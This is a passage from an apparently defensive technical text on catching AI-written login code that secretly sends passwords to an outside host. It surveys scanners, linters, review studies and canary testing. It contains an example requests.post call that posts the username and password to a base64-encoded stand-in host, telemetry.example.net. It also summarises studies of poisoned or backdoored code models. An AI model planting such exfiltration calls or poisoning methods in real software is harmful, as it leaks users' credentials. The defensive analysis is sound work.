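The malicious Python packages that Ryan and colleagues labelled show how common these signs are. The 370 packages, a random sample from a registry of 9,536, contained 90,527 lines of code, of which 6,413, or 7.1%, were malicious. The labels cover 47 indicators in seven types, with 2,962 occurrences in all:

| Type | Occurrences | Most common indicator |
|---|---|---|
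| How the code runs | 708 | Operating-system commands (244) |
| Evasion | 688 | Hidden errors (384) |
| Package description | 519 | Suspicious author details (222) |
| Effects on the computer | 411 | Collecting system information (217) |
| When the code runs | 291 | During installation (155) |
| Exfiltration | 174 | Sending stolen data such as keys (114) |
| Other network activity | 171 | Connecting to a suspicious host (76) |

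Encoding, such as base64, accounts for 226 occurrences, or 7.6% of the total. Network activity other than exfiltration accounts for 171, or 5.8%. A package can contain the same indicator several times, so these figures don't give the share of packages that encode text or contact a suspicious host. Hidden errors were the most common indicator, but many legitimate programs also hide errors, and Ryan and colleagues did not label any legitimate packages for comparison.

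Their taxonomy also includes "decoy functionality" (153 occurrences), which covers packages whose stated purpose hides what they do. One such package described itself as a library for building text interfaces.

Ryan and colleagues then looked for indicators that tend to follow one another. For two indicators A and B, they calculated the lift:

lift(A → B) = share of packages in which B directly follows A / (share with A × share with B)

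The lift is about 1 when two behaviors are unrelated. The highest value was 31.3, for connecting to a cryptocurrency mining service and then moving a file. Other strong pairs were disabling the certificate check and then downloading a program (17.4), stealing a file and then deleting it (13.3), and loading a module dynamically and then decrypting hidden code (9.4).

Ryan and colleagues present such sequences as the fingerprints of an attack, but some rest on very few cases. Connections to mining services occurred only twice in the sample, so the highest lift comes from at most two packages. They also inferred the order of each sequence from file positions and line numbers, which may differ from the order in which the code runs.

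The indicator closest to an exfiltration call in login code is the one for sending stolen data such as keys. None of the ten strongest pairs includes it, and the earlier login function would not match any of them.

### What encoding costs the attacker

Suppose the attacker encodes the address in that login function:

```python
requests.post(
    base64.b64decode(
        "aHR0cHM6Ly90ZWxlbWV0cnkuZXhhbXBsZS5uZXQvdjEvZXZlbnRz"
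    ).decode("utf-8"),
    json={"username": username, "password": password},
    timeout=5,
)
```

The request still goes to telemetry.example.net, but a reader no longer sees that name and a text search won't find it. The change also makes the code easier to detect by its structure. The plain request's syntax tree differed from a legitimate request's only in the text of the address, but here decoding calls replace the address. A scanner can look for decoding inside a network request, since legitimate login code rarely decodes the address it contacts.

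| Address | What a reader sees | What a scanner for obfuscation sees |
|---|---|---|
| Plain | An unfamiliar host | Nothing unusual |
| Encoded | No host | Decoding inside a network request |

*MalGuard* reports that most malicious packages mainly obfuscate the values they pass to functions, so the calls remain visible. A reviewer who lists every network call would therefore usually find an exfiltration call with an encoded address, and would only have to decode the address.

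In the Injective attack, encoding the address may even have made the code more suspicious. The decoded address, testnet.archival.chain.grpc-web.injective[.]network, looks like one of Injective's own test servers, so a reviewer might well have accepted it in plain text. A reviewer would be more likely to question a list of 49 numbers in a telemetry file.

Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors*, examined 6,420 malicious npm package versions and found that 80.3% used none of the eight evasion techniques they looked for. They attribute this to npm not requiring packages to be scanned before publication. A scanner that flagged only obfuscation would miss the plain request in the login function, just as it would have missed `checkValidityOfSeed`.

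A team can ban encoded addresses from its login code and enforce the ban with a scanner. An attacker who leaves the address in plain text to avoid the scanner then has to get it past the list of allowed destinations.

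## What general-purpose linters and scanners catch and miss

Many programming teams run a linter on every change, but a linter is unlikely to catch the password-stealing request in the earlier login function. Linter rules mostly describe mistakes, and this request is well-written code that uses HTTPS, leaves the certificate check on and times out after five seconds.

### How a linter rule works

Bandit is a security linter for Python with rules short enough to read in full. According to PyCQA's *Bandit*, the tool's page on PyPI, it builds a syntax tree from each file, runs its rules on the tree's nodes and writes a report. According to Bandit's *Test Plugins*, a developer adds a rule by picking a type of node, such as a function call, an import or a string, and writing a condition for it. When a node meets the condition, the rule returns a message, a severity rating for how much harm the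 problem could do, and a confidence rating for how likely the match is to be a real problem.

This invented rule follows that format:

```python
import bandit

@bandit.checks("Call")
def post_without_timeout(context):
    if (context.call_function_name_qual == "requests.post"
            and "timeout" not in context.call_keywords):
        return bandit.Issue(
            severity=bandit.MEDIUM,
            confidence=bandit.LOW,
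            text="This request has no time limit.",
        )
```

Bandit runs the rule on every Call node. The login function has two calls to `requests.post` and one to `reply.json`. The rule skips `reply.json` because the name doesn't match, and it returns nothing for the `requests.post` calls because both set a timeout.

If neither request had a timeout, the rule would return the same message for both, because it never reads the address.

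### Bandit's rules for network calls

Bandit's own timeout rule is slightly broader. Bandit's *B113* covers two HTTP libraries, requests and httpx, and also flags a timeout that the programmer has set to None. The worry is that a program without a time limit can hang forever. Bandit's *B501* describes a rule for requests that turn off the certificate check. Other rules come from a list of functions that Bandit flags wherever they appear, which Bandit's *blacklist_calls* sets out. Six rules are close enough to the login function's malicious request to be worth checking:

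| Rule | What it flags | Severity | The request to telemetry.example.net |
|---|---|---|---|
| B113 | A request with no time limit | Medium | Stops after five seconds |
| B501 | A request with the certificate check turned off | High | Leaves the check on |
| B310 | Opening an address with Python's own urllib library | Medium | Uses the requests library |
| B312 | Telnet, an old unencrypted protocol | High | Uses HTTPS |
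| B321 | FTP, an old protocol for moving files | High | Uses HTTPS |
| B323 | Connection settings that skip the certificate check | Medium | Uses the normal settings |

The request breaks none of them. Bandit also lists 44 rules, including B113 and B501, and none of their names refers to who receives a program's data.

B501 might look like a check on the recipient, but the owner of telemetry.example.net can get a valid certificate for that name.

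The rule with the most promising name is B105, on hardcoded passwords. According to Bandit's *B105*, it looks for passwords typed into the source, such as text assigned to a variable called `password`. In the login function, the user supplies the password at each login, so there is no such text to find.

If the programmer had used `urllib` instead of `requests`, B310 would have flagged the exfiltration call. The warning is meant to prompt someone to check that the URL can't use `file:` or another unexpected scheme. But B310 matches the function, not the host, so it would have flagged the request to the identity provider too.

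Bandit can flag legitimate parts of the login code while missing the exfiltration call. Its list of dangerous functions includes `hashlib.sha1`, which the breached-password lookup needs. Version 1.7.1 also treated any variable whose name began with "token_", in upper or lower case, as a possible password. Moving the identity provider's address into a constant called `TOKEN_URL` would have triggered a low-severity warning about a hardcoded password.

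### Clearing the warnings

Developers can easily clear a linter warning without checking where the request goes. Astral's *request-without-timeout (S113)* documents the same timeout rule in Ruff, another Python linter, and suggests adding a timeout of ten seconds.

If a model first wrote the login function with no timeouts, the linter would report two problems. The programmer, or a coding assistant told to fix the warnings, would add `timeout=5` to both requests, and the linter would then report no problems.

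Adding the timeout would also help the thief a little. Without it, a stalled server at telemetry.example.net could freeze every login, and someone would soon investigate. The timeout would limit each stall to five seconds, after which the login would fail with an error that names the host.

An empty Bandit report is still some evidence that code is free of familiar vulnerabilities. Bandit flags Python's ordinary random-number functions, which is useful in login code because an attacker may be able to predict a session token made with them. It flags ECB mode, the insecure setting that Schuster and colleagues made code-completion tools recommend, in one common encryption library. It also has rules for disabled certificate checks and services open on every network interface, two of the three unsafe patterns in the CodeTracer tests. A linter therefore has a reasonable chance of catching familiar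 vulnerabilities planted by a poisoned model, but very little chance of catching a cleanly written exfiltration call.

### Scanners built for malicious packages

GuardDog, an open-source scanner from the monitoring company Datadog, looks for signs that packages from PyPI, npm and similar sites are malicious. Two of its early rules for Python are relevant to exfiltration. The taint rule `exfiltrate-sensitive-data` follows data such as the computer's name or a file of cloud keys to a function that sends it over the network. The other rule, `shady-links`, flags web addresses with endings that attackers often use.

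These rules suit a package like gmgeoip, which read a system file and posted it to webhook.site. The login function receives its password as an argument, so a rule that tracks data from files and system details wouldn't flag it. A rule that flags suspicious top-level domains is also unlikely to help, because the function's address ends in .net, as millions of legitimate ones do. Such a rule would have been more likely to catch the xrpl.js attack, whose address ended in .xyz.

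Adding the password to the sources would help only if the team also supplied the allowed destinations, as in the earlier data-flow rule.

Package scanners are also designed for code written by strangers. A downloaded package that reads a secret from the computer's settings and sends it to another company is alarming. But a website that uses Cloudflare's CAPTCHA must send its secret key to Cloudflare in the same way, so a rule that is sensible for packages can raise false alarms on a company's own login service.

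GuardDog makes mistakes on packages too. It was one of the three scanners that wrongly flagged gen_wrappers, the harmless package that Guo and colleagues compared with gmgeoip. One example doesn't give an error rate, and a rate measured on public packages wouldn't apply directly to login code.

### Semgrep and CodeQL against human reviewers

Researchers have measured scanners' error rates on ordinary security flaws in generated code. Firouzi and Ghafari (2026), in *Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation*, compared Semgrep and CodeQL with human reviewers on 1,080 Python programs. The programs came from an earlier study in which GPT-4o answered each of 108 tasks ten times, writing code, criticising it and then improving it.

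Each task was designed to test for one weakness from MITRE's list of the 25 most dangerous. One trained reviewer labelled every program for that weakness alone. A second reviewer independently labelled one program per task, and a faculty expert settled any disagreement that the two couldn't resolve by discussion. Their agreement was very high, with a Cohen's kappa of 0.94. (Kappa corrects for agreement by chance, and 1 is a perfect score.)

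The reviewers judged 61% of the programs secure, compared with 60% for Semgrep and 80% for CodeQL. Semgrep's total was close to the reviewers' partly because it missed many vulnerable programs and flagged a similar number of secure ones.

Firouzi and Ghafari report each tool's recall (the share of vulnerable programs it flagged) and precision (the share of its flags that were correct). The approximate counts below are calculated from those figures for about 421 vulnerable programs and 659 secure ones.

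| Flagged by | Recall | Precision | Vulnerable programs missed | Secure programs flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CodeQL | 34% | 67% | 278 | 71 (11%) |
| Semgrep | 54% | 52% | 194 | 210 (32%) |
| Both tools | 30% | 76% | 295 | 40 (6%) |

Acting only on programs that both tools flagged would cut false alarms but miss 70% of the vulnerable programs. Acting on a flag from either tool would catch 34 + 54 − 30 = 58% of them and miss the other 42%.

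In the paper's main result, Semgrep agreed with the reviewers on 65% of programs and CodeQL on 61%. But the recall and precision in the table imply about 63% for Semgrep and 68% for CodeQL, which reverses the order. Both tools did poorly on either set of figures, since labeling every program secure would have been correct 61% of the time.

Neither tool flagged a program with a flawed redirect check. The program was supposed to send visitors only to example.com, but it matched the address against a text pattern instead of checking the host name directly. An address with an @ sign in the right place could have passed the test and sent visitors to another site. GPT-4o also often presented this code as secure, although it fixed the flaw once the researchers mentioned the risk. A team that writes its own check for allowed destinations can make the same mistake.

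The 1,080 programs are less varied than their number suggests, because the ten answers to each task tend to resemble each other. All the programs came from one model, now well out of date, prompted in one way. The tools often reported weaknesses other than the one a task was meant to test, but the reviewers considered only that one, so nobody checked whether the other reports were right.

Even so, the result matters beyond those two products. Firouzi and Ghafari reviewed nine papers from 2025 on the security or quality of generated code. Eight used such tools to judge the code, and four of those did so without human inspection. A published figure for how much generated code is "secure" may therefore include insecure code that the tools can't detect.

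These results don't measure how well scanners detect data theft. Every task concerned a known class of mistake, the flaws weren't deliberate, and a program counted as secure if it lacked one particular flaw. If CodeQL finds a third of the flaws that researchers chose from a standard list, there is little reason to expect it to do better on exfiltration calls, which its default Python queries don't appear to have a rule for.

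Two other 2026 papers tested scanners on deliberately planted code, though neither tested an exfiltration call. *Secret Stealing Attacks on Local LLM Fine-Tuning through Supply-Chain Model Code Backdoors* (Li, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) reports that Bandit, Semgrep and two other scanners raised no alerts on disguised model code that stole secrets from training data. In *Poison with Style* (Tran, Boshmaf and colleagues, 2026), Meta's CodeShield detected none of the planted vulnerabilities in three classes and about 74% in a fourth.

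### Ten malicious changes in 100,000

Even a scanner with much better error rates could be nearly useless, because malicious changes are so rare. In an illustrative example, a large company makes 100,000 changes to its code, 10 of which contain an exfiltration call. A general rule catches 90% of the malicious changes and wrongly flags only 1% of the harmless ones, a far lower rate than either tool had in the comparison with human reviewers.

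The rule catches 9 of the 10 malicious changes. It also flags 1% of the 99,990 harmless changes, or about 1,000. Only 9 of its about 1,009 alarms are real, a precision of about 0.9%.

The same calculation works for any rule. Let b be the share of changes that are malicious (the base rate), t the share of malicious changes that the rule catches, and f the share of harmless changes that it wrongly flags. Then:

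precision = tb / (tb + f(1 − b))

With t = 0.9, f = 0.01 and b = 0.0001, the precision is 0.0089, or 0.9%. Raising t to 1, so that the rule misses nothing, raises the precision only to about 1%. Lowering f helps far more. It would have to fall to about 0.009%, or 9 false alarms in 100,000 changes, for half of the alarms to be real.

If each alarm took ten minutes to check, all 1,009 would take 168 hours, or just over four working weeks. The reviewer would find one theft for every 112 alarms. Most people would start dismissing alarms after a glance long before they finished, and the real catch rate would fall below 90%.

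A project's own list of allowed destinations changes the result, because it gives the scanner a much narrower question. The rule now flags a change only if it sends a credential to a host that isn't on the list. Harmless changes rarely do that. The main exception is a change that connects a new supplier before anyone has added it to the list. Keeping the catch rate at 9 out of 10, the precision depends on how often this happens:

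| Rule | Real alarms | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| General rule | 9 | 1,000 | 0.9% |
| List, with 100 new suppliers not yet listed | 9 | 100 | 8% |
| List, with 20 | 9 | 20 | 31% |
| List, with 5 | 9 | 5 | 64% |

With 20 unlisted suppliers, the reviewer has 29 alarms to check, which takes less than five hours at the same pace. These alarms are also easier to resolve than a warning like "This request has no time limit", which isn't evidence of theft. An alarm like "the password goes to telemetry.example.net" includes the host, so the reviewer can check who owns it. If the owner is a real supplier, the team adds it to the list, and the host doesn't raise the alarm again.

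The catch rate wouldn't stay at 90% by itself. If the list permits too many hosts, the rule will miss thefts that use one of them, and tracking can lose the password before it reaches a request. A team without data-flow tools can use a cruder rule that reports every unlisted web address in the login code, whatever the program sends there. This needs only text matching, so an ordinary linter can run it. It will miss encoded addresses and raise more false alarms, but login code is short enough to keep the false alarms manageable.

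Most teams probably have no malicious changes to find, in which case every alarm is false, however good the rule is. How much work it takes to check alarms determines whether the team will still be paying attention when a real one arrives.

### What Rice's theorem rules out

No scanner can correctly decide, for every program, whether it sends a password to a host outside the list. In 1953 the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published a proof that, for any property of behaviour that some programs have and others lack, no tool can always determine in finite time whether an arbitrary program has it. Strictly, the theorem concerns what a program computes, but the requests it sends can count as part of its output.

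No tool can correctly determine, for every program, whether it will send a password over the network. For any program Q that does a calculation and never uses the network, someone could write a login function that first runs Q and then posts the password to telemetry.example.net. The function sends the password if and only if Q eventually finishes, so a perfect tool could be used to determine whether any such Q finishes. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can do this in every case.

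Scanning can still work. The theorem implies that every tool must fail on some programs, but these need not include the one a team cares about. Anyone who reads the earlier login function can see where both requests go, and a fairly simple tool can identify both destinations too.

A tool can also report every possible flow and accept false alarms, report only the flows it can confirm and miss some, or return "unknown", as the earlier data-flow rule does when it can't determine the host. In the example with Q, a tool that reports every possible flow wouldn't try to determine whether Q finishes. It would report the request because the program might reach it, which is what a reviewer wants for a login function.

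The team can also avoid this problem by restricting how its login code is written. Rice's theorem applies to how programs behave, not to how they are written. A tool can always check whether each call to `requests.post` has one of five approved addresses written out as its first argument. If the team also bans every other way of opening a connection in its login code, a reviewer can reject anything unusual without proving what it does. Authors will have to rewrite some harmless code that fails the check, but this is little work in a file that needs only a handful of requests. The approach is weaker for outside libraries, since the team can't choose how other people write them.

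Apart from the limit set by Rice's theorem, a scanner also needs the team's list of allowed destinations. Even if it could predict every request a program would make, it would need that list to distinguish the identity provider from an attacker's server.

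## Review by people and by language models

Unlike a linter, a person reviewing login code can ask why a request is there. The reviewer can also read the programmer's instructions to the model and the design of the surrounding system. In experiments, though, developers mostly checked whether generated code worked, and language models failed to flag most hostile code unless told to look for it.

### What a reviewer can use

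As in the earlier example, the programmer's instructions can show that the login function needs only the request to id.example.com. The system's design can give a reviewer another reason to object to the request to telemetry.example.net. If the design document assigns login counting to the company's own log server, the reviewer can object to that request as redundant without knowing who owns the host.

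A linter has only the file to work from, and even a scanner with a list of allowed destinations can only report that a host is missing from the list. A reviewer can ask the programmer about the host, and may also notice that the list is out of date, for example because it still includes a supplier the company has dropped.

A language model can use the task and the design too, but only if the team includes them in its prompt.

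### Thirty developers and a poisoned assistant

*Poisoned ChatGPT Finds Work for Idle Hands* (Oh et al., 2023) tested whether professional developers notice insecure suggestions from a tampered model. The 30 participants came from three software companies and had ten years' experience on average. Twelve worked mainly in security.

Each developer wrote three short Python programs to encrypt social security numbers, look up students in a database and find the IP address of a domain. Ten developers used a tool that generates code from a description, ten used a tool that completes code as they type, and ten had no AI tool. Oh and colleagues had poisoned the model behind both tools so that it suggested insecure code for these tasks. They did not tell the developers about the poisoning or the purpose of the study.

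The table gives the share of programs that contained each flaw. The figures in brackets are the share in which the flaw came from a poisoned suggestion.

| Flaw | Code generation | Code completion | No AI tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed encryption key | 100% (90%) | 80% (40%) | 44% |
| ECB encryption mode | 80% (80%) | 30% (30%) | 11% |
| Database command open to injection | 90% (90%) | 80% (30%) | 90% |
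| System command open to injection | 70% (70%) | 50% (30%) | 20% |

Across the four flaws, people with the generation tool accepted the poisoned code in 33 of 40 cases, compared with 13 of 40 for people with the completion tool. The database result is weak evidence of misplaced trust, because nine out of ten developers without an AI tool made the same mistake. The other three flaws were much rarer among those developers, so the poisoned tool probably caused many of the cases among its users.

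Most people in the generation group skimmed the code, ran it and submitted it if the output looked right. Four of them weren't confident that they understood it. One security specialist using the completion tool chose a secure encryption mode, ran into an unrelated error, and accepted ECB, an insecure mode, while fixing it. The victim of the 2024 wallet theft also missed the private key during several rounds of debugging.

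The specialists didn't do clearly better than the others. None of the eight specialists who had an AI tool used a secure key, compared with two of the twelve other developers. With the generation tool, two of four specialists avoided the flawed system command, as did one of six others. When asked afterwards, most specialists knew about the security problems but said they had concentrated on making the programs work in the time available. These groups are too small to rule out a moderate advantage for specialists.

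Oh and colleagues also surveyed 238 people, mostly students, about why they trusted or distrusted such tools. Most answers concerned whether the code worked, and only three people mentioned security as a reason for distrust.

### A newer experiment with ChatGPT

In *Beware EviLLM*, Ryu, Chung and colleagues (2026) tested 21 people with experience in programming and cybersecurity. The attack in this experiment caused the user to receive vulnerable code. It worked through the user's ChatGPT account or browser, without any tampering with the model.

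In the account version, 7 of 8 people didn't notice the vulnerabilities, and in the browser version, 10 of 13 didn't, for a total of 17 of 21 (81%). The groups were small, and a result of 7 out of 8 is compatible with a true miss rate between about 50% and nearly 100%. After experiencing the attack, 13 of the 21 reported that they rarely or never considered the risk of one.

Both experiments planted vulnerabilities rather than exfiltration calls, so the 81% doesn't estimate how many people would miss an exfiltration call. Such a call might be easier to notice, because anyone can see an unfamiliar host name, whereas recognising ECB as a mistake takes some knowledge of cryptography. It might also be harder, because requests to unfamiliar hosts are often legitimate.

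The developers in Oh and colleagues' study were also writing programs under a time limit. A reviewer whose only task is to check a login change may be more careful. But running the code and checking its output, as many of those developers did, would not expose an exfiltration call.

### Language models that look for malicious packages

Language models have done much better than this at finding malicious packages, at least when the package is small. In a large one, they can miss a few hostile lines among thousands of harmless ones. Gao, Peng and colleagues (2026), in *Efficient Code Analysis via Graph Representation Learning-Guided Large Language Models*, present a system called GMLLM that first selects the code most worth reading. It works in four steps:

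1. It turns a Python package into a graph. The nodes are modules, classes and functions, and the edges are calls and dependencies.
2. It checks each node against a list of sensitive behaviours, most of which a language model wrote after reading sample packages, and records the matches.
3. A small neural network classifies the graph as malicious or harmless. Its training data needs only that one label for each package.
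4. If the network's answer is "malicious", GMLLM works out which parts of the graph influenced it most. It passes the 20 most influential edges, with the code they connect, to a language model, which gives the final verdict and describes any hostile code it finds.

Gao and colleagues compared GMLLM with GPT-4o reading the packages directly. On their own collection of packages, the results were:

| Package size | Recall, GPT-4o alone | Recall, GMLLM with GPT-4o | Precision, GPT-4o alone | Precision, GMLLM with GPT-4o |
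|---|---|---|---|---|
| Small | 97.4% | 99.3% | 94.1% | 98.4% |
| Medium | 98.3% | 97.5% | 93.5% | 96.1% |
| Large | 67.3% | 87.2% | 76.2% | 89.1% |
| All | 89.3% | 95.3% | 89.5% | 95.1% |

The improvement was greatest for large packages. For medium ones, GMLLM caught slightly fewer malicious packages but raised fewer false alarms. On three public collections, its recall was 93% to 97% and its precision was about 95%. The choice of language model mainly affected precision. With Llama 3 in place of GPT-4o, recall on the whole collection rose to 97.7%, but precision fell to 71.9%, so more than a quarter of the alarms were false.

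GMLLM reached 95% precision only because so many of the test packages were malicious, about 45% as calculated from the published rates. It wrongly flagged 4.1% of the harmless packages. In the earlier example of 100,000 code changes with 10 malicious ones, the same rates would mean catching nine or ten of the malicious changes and raising about 4,100 false alarms, a precision of roughly 0.2%.

The main results separate packages by size but not by whether their code was plain or obfuscated. Gao and colleagues cite a 2024 study by Fang and colleagues in which language models did well on simple code but struggled with complex or obfuscated code. An exfiltration call in a login function is short and often plain, so a language model should handle it well. But the high recall on small packages may depend on signs that the login function lacks, such as code that starts other programs.

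GPT-4o is also an old model. Gao and colleagues tried GMLLM with two newer ones, Qwen3.5-Flash and DeepSeek-V3.2, on part of the collection and report that it still improved detection.

### Models with another job to do

A coding assistant usually reads code to complete some other task, without being asked to look for malware. Shao, Ren and colleagues tested models in this situation in *Your Agent May Misevolve* (2025). They inserted malicious code into eight popular GitHub projects to make 371 samples. They then gave each sample to an agent to package as a tool for its own use, and the safe response was to refuse.

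All six models in the test rarely refused. GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B each refused one of the 371 samples (0.27%). Qwen3-235B refused the most, at 27 samples (7.28%).

Shao and colleagues then added an instruction to assess each project's safety and refuse to package unsafe ones. Qwen3-235B's refusal rate rose to 69.0%, and Gemini 2.5 Flash's rose from 2.70% to 68.5%, so each still accepted nearly a third of the samples. Both models could apparently recognise much of the hostile code but didn't act on it without that instruction.

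These refusal rates measure only recall. Every sample was malicious, so a model that refused everything would have scored 100%. Part of the increase may come from the models refusing more often in general, including on harmless projects.

### A content filter and 3,671 malicious programs

Some companies put a second model between a language model and its users to block harmful text. Chen and colleagues tested one such filter on code from their scam benchmark. They used NeMo Guardrails, NVIDIA's toolkit for adding such checks, with Llama Nemotron Safety Guard V2, a model that classifies text as safe or unsafe.

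The filter received 3,671 programs with malicious addresses, written by the seven models released in 2025. It flagged five of them, or 0.14%. It flagged at most 0.3% of any one model's programs, and none from four of the models.

The five detections don't look like real successes either. The filter classified three of the programs as criminal planning and two as sexual content involving minors. It assigned none of them to its categories for fraud, malware or the use of scam websites.

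The test was fair if the question is whether the safety filter blocks code that contacts a scam site. Someone might reasonably expect it to, particularly when the filter's own categories mention scam sites. Chen and colleagues showed that it doesn't, so a team shouldn't rely on it for that protection.

The test is much less informative about whether language models can review code. The filter was given the program and a list of 24 categories, many about subjects such as violence, harassment and profanity. It was not given the programmer's request or a list of approved hosts, and it could not look up addresses. Code that sends an API key to the service that issued it looks normal unless the reader knows that the service is a scam. By definition, at least one of the three address detectors had flagged each of these programs.

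A fairer test would give the reviewing model the request and the results of an address lookup. It would also include harmless programs, because the published test can't measure how often the filter blocks them.

### Why a reviewing model may miss the call

A model reviewing code may accept the purpose that names and comments suggest. Misleading names hinder human readers, and they could easily mislead a model too, since most of the code it learned from has accurate names. Direct evidence is limited. Li and colleagues found that neither Gemini 3 Pro, in 20 audits, nor GPT-5.6 Sol, in 10, identified a planted data theft. Both models described the code as unusual engineering or data maintenance. The planted code made no outgoing request, so the result doesn't show how well either model would check the hosts that code contacts.

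A better test would show a model the same function with accurate names and with misleading ones. Until someone runs that test, a team can, as a precaution, have the reviewing model describe what the code does without seeing its comments or original function names. Converting Python code to a syntax tree and back removes the comments, and a short script can replace the function names with neutral ones.

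The lack of a list of approved hosts is a more certain problem. Without one, a model must guess whether a host is approved from the host's name or from what it remembers about the host. This follows from the definition of an exfiltration call. None of the tests described here measured how much a list would improve a model's reviews.

The reviewing model may have learned from the same scam pages as the model that wrote the code. In the original tests by Chen and colleagues, GPT-4o and GPT-4o-mini had 2,726 malicious domains in common, while GPT-4o and DeepSeek-V3, which come from different companies, had 2,689. Using another company's model as the reviewer may therefore add less protection than it seems to. If two models each miss 30% of malicious requests, both will miss 9% if their mistakes are independent, but 30% if they make the same mistakes.

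Chen and colleagues measured the overlap by counting the addresses that models wrote, but its effect on review is conjecture. A model that writes a scam address might still recognise it when asked about it. Their preprint contains slight evidence of this. Gemini 2.5 Pro's content filter blocked 50% of the requests that named a known scam site and 37% of the others, so including the name may have helped the filter.

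### Asking for hosts instead of a verdict

A reviewing model can answer the question "Is this code safe?" with a plain yes, which leaves the team nothing to check. A more useful instruction asks for facts:

```
List every place in this change that can open a network connection.
For each one, give:
- the file and line number
- the full host name, or "unknown" if a setting or variable decides it
- every value sent in the address, headers and body
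- where each of those values comes from
- what the program does with the response
Do not judge whether the change is safe.
```

For the earlier login function, a correct answer would contain these facts:

| Line | Host | Values sent | Source of the values | Response |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 5 | id.example.com | Username, password | The function's arguments | Used to decide whether the login succeeds |
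| 10 | telemetry.example.net | Username, password | The function's arguments | Discarded |

The team can check each row against the source code and search the syntax tree for missing rows. Here the search finds two calls to `requests.post`, so an answer with one row would be incomplete. A short program can then compare the hosts and values with the list of allowed destinations. The result doesn't depend on whether the model classifies telemetry.example.net as trustworthy, and a reassuring comment in the code affects it less.

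This method still depends on the model finding connections that a simple search misses, such as those inside a library.

None of the studies described here compared asking for a list of hosts with asking a general question. Shao and colleagues came closest by comparing a prompt that didn't mention safety with one that asked for a general safety assessment. The large difference in results shows that wording matters, but not that asking for a list of hosts works better.

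A team can compare the instructions on its own code. It could take 40 old login changes that it trusts, add a request to a reserved domain such as example.net to 20 of them, and give all 40 to the model with each instruction. Nobody needs to run the altered code. The team should count missed requests and false alarms separately. With only 20 planted requests, it could detect a large difference between the instructions but not a small one.

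### A review procedure for a login change

The steps below combine the inventory of destinations with information that only a reviewer has. The reviewer follows them in order and sends the change back as soon as one fails.

| Step | Question | Evidence required | Reject the change if |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Task | Which requests does the task need? | The programmer's instructions to the model, the system's design, and a list that the reviewer writes before reading the code | Nobody can say what the change was supposed to do |
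| 2. Extent | What else did the change alter? | All changed files, including settings and libraries | It alters something that the task didn't require |
| 3. Readability | Can a person read all of it? | Plain source code for every file | It hides an address or program code by encoding it |
| 4. Connections | Which lines can open a connection? | One list from the reviewer and another from a language model | The lists still differ after a second look |
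| 5. Destinations | Which host does each connection reach, and who controls it? | The live server's settings and the supplier's official documentation | A host isn't on the list of allowed destinations, or its owner is unknown |
| 6. Data | What does each request send? | A trace from every secret to the address, headers and body | A host would receive data that the list doesn't allow |
| 7. Reason | Why does the login need this request? | A requirement in the design, or an explanation from a colleague who relies on the request | The only explanation is a name, a comment or the model's own answer |
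| 8. Release | Will this exact code run on the live server? | A build from the approved version | The released files differ from that build |

The reviewer should list the expected requests (step 1) before opening the code, because seeing a finished answer makes it harder to think of another. One developer in the study by Oh and colleagues noticed that starting with the poisoned tool kept her from considering other solutions, so she wrote a later program without it, and that program was secure. This is one person's experience, but the list takes only a minute or two to write.

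For the login function, the list from step 1 has one entry, the request to id.example.com. The change passes steps 2 and 3 because it affects one file and hides nothing. In step 4, the reviewer finds connections on lines 5 and 10, and in step 5 rejects the change because telemetry.example.net isn't on the list of allowed destinations.

If the host belongs to a new analytics supplier, the team can add it to the list and allow it to receive a count of logins. The change would then pass step 5 but fail step 6, because the request sends passwords.

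A language model can help with steps 4 and 6, where a person can check its answers against the code. People should make the decisions in steps 5 and 7, since those depend on contracts and on what colleagues need. The reviewer shouldn't be the person who asked the model for the code, because that person has already seen it work and may be in a hurry to finish. Several specialists in the 2023 study blamed a lack of time for their mistakes, so a team should perhaps reserve the full procedure for code that handles credentials and allow enough time for it.

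Step 8 is easy to forget because the review seems to be over by then. It guards against attacks like the one on xrpl.js, in which the published package differed from the code on GitHub.

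## Observing and blocking connections at run time

A program must produce the real address before it can connect, so anyone monitoring its connections can see where a request goes, even if the source code hides it. In one version of the campaign that Microsoft described, a file disguised as the jQuery library decoded a base64 address when a project's development server started. Microsoft's monitoring software still recorded `node server/server.js` contacting price-oracle-v2[.]vercel[.]app.

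*Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine* (Hall and Engelbrecht, 2026), written for Mozilla's 0DIN security programme, shows that a coding agent can end up running hostile code that isn't in any of the project's files.

Before release, a team can run the login service in a closed environment and log in with a fake password. Once the service is live, the team can limit which hosts it may contact. These limits are a form of egress control, which restricts a program's outgoing connections through rules enforced outside the program.

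### A login with a canary credential

A canary credential is a fake secret planted so that its appearance in network traffic reveals a leak. The test has five steps:

1. Put the login service in an environment with no route to the internet, and start recording before the service starts.
2. Redirect every name lookup and connection to stand-in servers.
3. Log in with a canary username and password.
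4. Compare every host in the recording with the list of allowed destinations.
5. Search the decrypted addresses, headers and bodies for the canary.

*Accelerating Incident Response* (2026) describes a sandbox of this kind for Linux programs. Each program runs in an isolated Docker container with no internet access. All its outgoing traffic goes to a second container, where FakeNet-NG imitates common network services and records everything it receives. The system runs only programs that a classifier has labelled as possibly stealing data. Using the same filter for login code would be risky, because a cleanly written login function might never reach the sandbox.

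The stand-in servers have to reply as the real ones would. The earlier login function sends a request to id.example.com before it makes the exfiltration call. If nothing answers, `requests.post` raises an error and the function stops there, so the recording doesn't show the exfiltration call. The stand-in for id.example.com should therefore return status code 200 and a session token, which can also be a canary.

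The stand-ins can decrypt HTTPS requests if the login service trusts their test certificate. Python's requests library accepts one through the setting `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE`. If the service has to reach a real supplier during the test, the team can use a decrypting proxy. Pye used one in *What data do coding agents send, and where to?* to study seven coding agents in 2025. The agent, the proxy and the DNS server each ran in a separate restricted environment. Some parts of the agents ignored their proxy settings, so Pye redirected the traffic at network level to avoid missing requests.

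The canary should be long, random and made only of letters and digits, so that it won't turn up by chance and formats such as JSON won't alter it. The search should also cover its common hashes and encodings. Base64 converts three bytes at a time, so the same canary can produce three different patterns depending on where it starts in the text. Decoding every base64 string in the traffic and searching the results is easier than searching for all three patterns.

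For the login function, the log should look like this:

| Event | Host | Canary found | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | id.example.com | None | Allowed |
| POST to /v1/verify | id.example.com | Username and password, in the body | Allowed |
| Name lookup | telemetry.example.net | None | Host not on the list |
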